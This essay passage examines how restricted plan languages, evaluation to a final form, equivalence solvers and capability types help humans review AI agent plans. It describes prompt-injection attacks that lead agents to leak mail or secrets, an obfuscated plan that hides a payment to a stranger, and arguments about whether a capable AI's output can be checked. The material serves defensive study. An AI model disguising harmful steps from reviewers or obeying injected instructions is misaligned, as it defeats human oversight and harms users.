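The text of a restricted plan shows a reviewer every call the plan can make, whereas many approval prompts for coding agents leave out some of what will run. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* gives the example of a prompt to approve `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine but runs whatever the script contains. If a plan can act only by calling tools by name, a reviewer who approves three calls has approved only those three.

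Meijer wants to go further and show users the plan in plain English. His agents write plans as structured data, which ordinary software can translate into sentences. The office assistant's three-line plan might come out like this:

> Fetch the unpaid invoices and take the first. Pay the amount on that invoice to the account on it. Email finance the word "Paid" and the invoice number.

An employee who can't program could check these sentences. They also stay consistent with the plan, because software generates them from the same data that the interpreter runs.

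This holds only if the software ignores everything else the model wrote. In Meijer's example of the pattern `*.txt`, the model's own description of the step mentions only `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. His readable version of an email theft is worse, because it repeats an excuse from the attacker's text in a tool description. It tells the user that the assistant will send a summary of her mail to an outside address "for compliance purposes". A translation based only on the calls and their arguments would leave out the excuse.

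### Evaluating a plan to its final form

Gonzalez announced the configuration language Dhall in 2016 on the blog Haskell for all, partly in response to the complaint that programmable settings files become unreadable. Every Dhall program finishes, so software can fully evaluate any file, and people can read the result instead of the code. Her example is a deliberately obscure file that uses imported functions to build a list of three zombies and two police officers. The compiler reduces it to the number of characters, five, and the protagonist, a police officer named Leon.

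The same treatment works on an agent's plan. Suppose the office assistant writes this:

```
codes = [1, 3, 7, 7]
supplier = "account-"
for i in range(4):
    supplier = supplier + str(codes[3 - i])
total = 0
for i in range(19):
    total = total + 500
if total > 9000:
    pay(supplier, total)
else:
    send_email("finance", "Nothing to pay")
```

A tired reviewer might see a supplier, a total and a polite message to finance, and approve it. But the first loop reads the list backwards and adds 7, 7, 3 and 1 to the account name. The second loop adds 500 nineteen times, which makes 9,500. The condition is therefore true, and the message to finance disappears. What remains is one line:

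```
pay("account-7731", 9500)
```

This is the plan from the earlier examples that pays a stranger. The software found it without calling any tools, so nobody lost money.

Evaluation stops at any value that only a tool can supply. Take a plan that pays too much:

```
invoice = read_invoices()[0]
total = invoice.amount
for i in range(3):
    total = total + 100
pay(invoice.account, total)
```

The invoice is unknown until the plan runs, so the final form still contains it:

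```
invoice = read_invoices()[0]
pay(invoice.account, invoice.amount + 100 + 100 + 100)
```

The reviewer can now see the extra 300, but not whose account will receive the money. Dhall handles unknown values the same way. Gonzalez shows a function that makes ten copies of an element, which the compiler reduces to a list of ten copies before anyone has specified the element.

The final form may also be longer than the plan. A three-line loop that makes a million payments turns into a million lines. If a plan makes ten tool calls that each return yes or no, and adds to a total after each yes, writing out every case takes 1,024 versions. Gonzalez points out that, for settings files, a declared type limits how complicated the result can be. A plan language could likewise declare a maximum number of calls, so the reviewer would know that limit before reading the plan.

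The company also has to run the final form that the reviewer approved. Dhall files can import functions from a web address. If a plan did the same, the code at that address could change between approval and execution.

Termination helps reviewers less than it seems to. Software could simplify an obscure plan by evaluating it early just as well if the agent had written it in Python, provided that the software paused at every tool call and stopped after, say, a million steps. Gonzalez concedes that a Dhall file can take longer than the age of the universe to evaluate, though she thinks people are unlikely to write one by accident. Evaluating a plan early is safe because the computation between tool calls has no effects on the world. It is not safe in a language that lets any line open a file or contact the network, even if all programs in that language finish.

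### Comparing two versions

Reviewers often see a plan more than once, because they ask for a change and the agent rewrites it. A list of changed lines may not help, since the amount of text changed doesn't reliably indicate how much the plan's behaviour has changed.

Amazon's policy language Cedar shows what a solver can do here. A Cedar policy isn't a plan. It states who may do what to which resource, and software consults it whenever a request arrives. *Cedar* (2024) explains that the designers kept the language small enough for an exact translation into logic, so that a company can reorganise its policies and confirm that nobody's permissions have changed. According to *How We Built Cedar* (2024), the software turns each set of policies into a formula and asks a solver for a request that one set allows and the other refuses. If A and B are the two formulas, the solver looks for a way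 to satisfy

(A ∧ ¬B) ∨ (¬A ∧ B)

If no request satisfies it, the two sets are equivalent.

Say a company allows payments when the amount is at most 500, and an agent rewrites the condition as "less than 501". If amounts are whole numbers, both versions allow the same payments. If amounts can include pence, a solver will find a payment that only the new version allows, such as 500.50. The reviewer then only has to decide whether that payment matters, which is much easier than rereading both versions. The same method works for plans without loops that use only linear arithmetic, because whether two such plans make the same calls is decidable.

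Cedar also shows that a readable text can mislead someone who doesn't know the language's rules. Cedar refuses a request if any "forbid" policy applies, but it ignores any policy that causes an error during evaluation. A reviewer may therefore believe that a "forbid" policy protects something when an error has disabled it. Cedar's designers judged its policies at least as readable as those of two rival languages, but they describe this judgement as subjective.

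### Smaller plans

Shorter plans ought to be easier to check, and tests of Soteria offer some evidence that they are. When the planner could use a library of verified sub-plans, its median plan shrank from 11 states to 8, far more plans passed verification, and the share that passed at the first attempt rose from 23.3% to 48.5%. The remaining failures were mostly syntax errors, which the planner could repair easily. Without the library, the planner often broke the same rule on consecutive attempts.

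These figures come from one model on airline tasks, with a program verifier as the reviewer. A person might gain less, because they would have fewer steps to read but would also have to know what each sub-plan does or trust its contract.

The plans became smaller because He and colleagues added sub-plans, which work much like functions in ordinary programming, to the language. Some restricted languages, including Girrens and Wang's, ban user-defined functions, so their plans have to repeat the same steps wherever they are needed. A restriction that helps a checker follow data through a plan can therefore give a human reviewer more to read.

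### What people do with plans they can read

Most agents don't ask people to approve plans. The survey *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) counts 15 commercial systems that ask for permission while they run, and most of them ask about single commands or calls. Claude Code, for instance, asks about every command it wants to run in a terminal. A few systems ask about more at once. The coding agent Devin asks people to approve its plan and, later, to separately approve the finished code.

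Asking about every command wears people out. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* looked at the part that user review played in a larger set of 290 incident reports, and found that it contributed to 105 of them. In 80 reports, users had switched on automatic approval, often because the alternative was hundreds of prompts per session. In 31, the prompt didn't tell users what they needed to know. (Some reports involved both.)

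Agent users interviewed and surveyed for *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) said they had given up reading permission details because of time pressure, fatigue or too much information. The paper therefore warns against treating repeated approval as a sign of growing trust, since it may be habit. However, *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) cites usage data showing that experienced users of Claude Code turned on automatic approval more often than beginners but also interrupted the agent more often. They may have been watching the work instead of reading prompts.

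Restricted plans have an advantage over this, because a reviewer makes one decision about a complete plan, and each line of the plan corresponds to an effect. However, an experiment on plans in plain language gives reason to doubt that reviewers then make better decisions.

*Plan-Then-Execute* (He, Demartini and Gadiraju, 2025) analysed how 248 people recruited online worked with an assistant on six everyday tasks, such as setting alarms and exchanging currency. The assistant ran on an older model, GPT-3.5-turbo. It first wrote a numbered plan in short sentences, then turned each main step into one action in a simulated environment. The researchers chose three tasks for which the assistant's plan was correct and three for which it was flawed. Some participants could edit the plan, some could check and correct each action, some could do both, and 63 could do neither. Every participant said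 whether they trusted the plan to produce a correct outcome.

The table gives the trust of the 63 participants who could do neither, then the share of tasks that ended correctly for them and for the 60 who could do both.

| Task | Plan | Trusted the plan | Correct result, no involvement | Correct result, editing and checking |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Two currency exchanges | Flawed | 89% | 0% | 13% |
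| Credit card repayment | Flawed | 79% | 78% | 75% |
| Television repair | Flawed | 90% | 44% | 52% |
| Alarms | Correct | 94% | 95% | 82% |
| Return flight | Correct | 87% | 98% | 90% |
| Trip to Japan | Correct | 81% | 6% | 22% |

These participants trusted the flawed plans 86% of the time on average and the correct plans 87% of the time, so their trust was almost unrelated to the plan's quality. The flawed credit card plan usually worked, which partly excuses their trust in it. The flawed currency exchange plan never worked, because it put both exchanges into a single step and the assistant performed one action per step, so one of the exchanges never happened.

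Letting people edit the plan didn't help much. It improved the currency plan slightly, but people also damaged plans that had been correct. With the alarms, the share of correct results fell from 95% to 75% when participants could edit the plan but not check the actions. Checking the actions helped most with the trip to Japan, where the plan was fine but the assistant tended to choose an itinerary that didn't match the request. Overall, people who did both found the work more demanding and were right 56% of the time, compared with 54% for people who did neither. The researchers suspect the plans were too plausible, since they had a clear structure and covered most of what the task required. One participant wrote of seeing no room for improvement.

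This suggests that plain sentences are not enough, because the plans in the study were already plain sentences, without loops or code. It is weaker evidence against restricted languages. If the language had required every step to be exactly one tool call, nobody could have merged two exchanges into one step, and a simple checker would have caught the mistake anyway. The participants also had little reason to be careful, since the money was imaginary and a good plan or a correct result earned them a bonus of £0.05.

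### An experiment on the language itself

None of these studies gave people the same plans in a restricted and an unrestricted language, so they can't show how much the restriction helps. Researchers could test this by preparing harmless and harmful plans for a set of office tasks and writing each plan in four forms: ordinary Python, a restricted language, the restricted plan evaluated to its final form, and a translation into sentences. The harmful plans should include different kinds of mistakes, such as an extra payment, a missing approval, a pattern that matches too many files and a duplicate invoice. Reviewers would see each plan in only one form and decide whether to let it run.

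The important result would be the gap between the share of harmful plans that reviewers reject and the share of harmless plans they reject, since a language that makes reviewers suspicious of everything would raise both. The researchers should also let an agent write its own plans in each language, because a plan in the restricted language may be longer than a Python plan for the same job.

Harmful plans should be rare in such a test, as they are at work. Suppose one plan in a thousand is harmful, and a careful reviewer rejects 60% of the harmful plans and 5% of the harmless ones. In a thousand plans, the reviewer would reject about 50 harmless ones and have a 60% chance of rejecting the harmful one, which is roughly 83 false alarms for every harmful plan caught. Few people would stay careful for long under those conditions, so a test in which half the plans are harmful would make every language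 look better than it is. I expect the final form to do best against hidden computation and all four forms to do equally badly against the duplicate invoice.

### Reading the steps and foreseeing the consequences

Even a reviewer who understands every step may not know what the plan will lead to. Eliezer Yudkowsky, a co-founder of MIRI, gave an extreme version of this argument in his 2022 essay *AGI Ruin: A List of Lethalities*. He claimed that if a highly capable AI's output could end the danger from other AI systems, people could not make sure it was safe by checking it first. He argued that such a plan would work because the AI knew something about the world that people did not, so they couldn't predict all its results.

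One reply is that checking an answer is often much easier than finding it. Anyone can check a completed sudoku, and Meijer's proposal relies on proofs that are hard to find but easy to check. But a sudoku has exact rules, and nobody has written down exactly what would count as a good outcome for the world. The reply therefore works for the parts of a plan whose requirements somebody can specify, while Yudkowsky's claim is about the other parts.

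His argument has much less force for everyday plans, which seldom depend on knowledge that no human has. They do often depend on knowledge that the reviewer lacks. Suppose the office assistant proposes to replace an old password for the billing system:

```
reset_password("billing")
```

A step that changes a password is easy to read and sounds like good practice. But if the nightly backup program still logs in with the old password, the backups will stop, and perhaps nobody will notice for weeks. Somebody in the company could have predicted this, so the remedy is to send the plan to that person, or to have software list every program that uses the password. With a plan of the kind Yudkowsky describes, nobody would be able to predict the harm.

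Reviewers of ordinary plans would therefore gain more from information about effects than from a simpler language. For `delete_file("*.txt")`, a list of the files that currently match would help. *Let the Agent Do It?* suggests that permission prompts should also show whether an action can be undone. A company can provide both for plans in any language, as long as its software can determine which tools a plan will call.

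### Which restriction helps the reviewer

Restricted plan languages usually combine several bans, and the easiest way to compare what each does for a reader is to lift them one at a time. Start with unbounded loops:

```
while not bank_confirms(invoice.number):
    wait(60)
```

A reviewer can't tell whether this loop will end, but can see that it only queries the bank and waits, so the worst outcome is a plan that hangs. If the loop contained `pay`, the reviewer would have good reason to object, and the same would be true of a bounded loop containing `pay` with a very high iteration limit.

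Now allow code built at run time:

```
run(message.body)
```

The reviewer can't tell what this line will do, because that depends on the email. The rest of the plan doesn't help either, since the email's code might undo or repeat any of it.

Finally, allow effects that the plan doesn't declare:

```
summary = tidy(invoices)
```

If `tidy` is a library function that also uploads the invoices somewhere, the line that calls it looks like harmless computation. To find the upload, the reviewer would have to read the library and everything it calls.

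The ban on undeclared effects probably helps a human reviewer most. It lets them skip every line that only computes, so in a sixty-line plan with four calls, they only have to think about the four calls. It also makes it safe to evaluate the plan to a final form. A language also needs the ban on code built at run time, because that ban lets the reviewer trust the declared effects. The ban on unbounded loops helps much less than the other two. It guarantees that evaluation will end, which spares the reviewer from judging whether a loop will, but a time limit gives most of the same benefit.

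### Types that track authority

If undeclared effects are the main problem, a language could forbid those and keep everything else. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) try this in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, using an experimental feature of the type system in Scala 3, a general-purpose language that allows recursion and unbounded loops. A type normally states what kind of value something is, such as a number or text. With this feature, it also records which capabilities the value can use. A capability is an object in the program that grants access to something, such as a file or the network.

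In this notation, a function that takes text, returns text and does nothing else has the type `String -> String`. If the function also uses an email tool called `mail`, its type becomes `String ->{mail} String`. The compiler works out these types and rejects the program before it runs if a function uses a capability that its type doesn't list. A plan therefore can't hide an upload in a function called `tidy`, because the function's type would have to list the upload capability.

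Secrets come wrapped in a container that accepts only functions with no capabilities. The agent can trim a password or count its characters, but the result stays in the container. It can't email the password, because a function that sends email needs a capability. An agent could normally get around these rules with features that let a program ignore types or inspect itself while it runs, so its code must compile in a "safe mode" that bans them.

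The design changes what a person has to review. In one of the paper's examples, an agent compares confidential contracts and writes a summary. The programmer gives it a database of documents, a file for the summary, a tool for comparing texts and a language model that can only summarise. Odersky and colleagues want to be sure that the agent can't leak the contracts, even if nobody reads its code. A person reads the short list of what the agent can access, and the compiler checks every program against it. The same list covers many plans, so the reviewer reads it once carefully instead of approving a new plan every few minutes.

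To test this, they gave agents a software project with a folder of secrets and ran 131 trials with each of two models. The trials combined ordinary tasks with hidden instructions from an attacker, and added 11 tasks in which the user tried to obtain the secrets. With the protection on, no secret reached the agent's output. Without it, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in two of the 11 malicious tasks and MiniMax M2.5 in eight. As with Soteria, the perfect score mostly confirms that the software enforces what it was designed to enforce. The finding that the agents could still do their work is more informative. On simulated customer service, three models had completion rates 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher when writing Scala than when calling tools directly. On a set of real software problems, the one model they tested did slightly worse with Scala, at 41.7% against 43.3% with direct tool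 calls.

The guarantee covers access and leaks but not whether the agent does the right thing. The paper lists wrong results among its non-goals, so a plan that pays a duplicate invoice would compile. The type system also doesn't check commands that the agent starts outside Scala, and the agent could leak secrets through timing or by failing to finish. A terminating language would prevent the second kind of leak, which is one of the few protections that a ban on unbounded loops would add to these types.

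### What the restrictions cost

Banning unbounded loops restricts office work very little. Vartanian notes that programmers mostly use them for programs that wait indefinitely for events, calculations that repeatedly refine an approximate answer, and data nested to unknown depth. Few office plans need any of these, and a plan that waits for the bank can stop waiting after an hour.

Bans on functions are more limiting. CaMeL's restricted Python doesn't let agents define their own functions, and Odersky and colleagues explain that lifting the ban would be hard. CaMeL tracks each piece of data as the program runs. If programs can pass functions to other functions, the time needed to predict precisely in advance where data will go can grow exponentially with the length of the program. Types avoid this problem because each function's type describes what the function uses, so the compiler can check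 functions one by one.

One might expect an agent that can use all of Scala to complete more tasks than one limited to restricted Python. Odersky and colleagues compared the results of their system, TACIT, with CaMeL's published results on the four areas of the AgentDojo benchmark. The table shows the share of tasks each system completed.

| Area | Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | o4-mini, CaMeL | o4-mini, TACIT |
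|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 62.5% | 59.0% |
| Office work | 53.8% | 50.5% | 81.4% | 52.9% |
| Workplace chat | 48.6% | 40.0% | 68.6% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 74.3% | 68.6% |

Except on travel with Gemini, where CaMeL's performance collapsed, agents using the restricted language did about as well or better. With o4-mini they did better in all four areas. The systems differ in many other ways, so the comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the language, but it doesn't suggest that restricted Python makes agents perform worse on tasks like these.

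The other drawback is that a checker may reject safe plans. Nikolaou and colleagues acknowledge that CaMeLoT's simplified treatment of loops may do this. Suppose a rule requires every run to email finance, and a plan loops over a fixed list of three people in that department, emailing each one. If the checker's model allows a run to leave the loop before the first round, the checker will find a run with no emails and reject the plan, though every real run sends three. Evaluating the plan first would avoid this false alarm by turning the loop into three separate calls.

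People who run into many such rejections can easily switch to an agent without the restrictions, and the 80 reports in which users had switched off approval prompts suggest that many would. A stricter language doesn't protect people who have stopped using it, so designers have good reason to drop restrictions that mostly irritate people and keep the ones that let a reviewer trust the list of calls.
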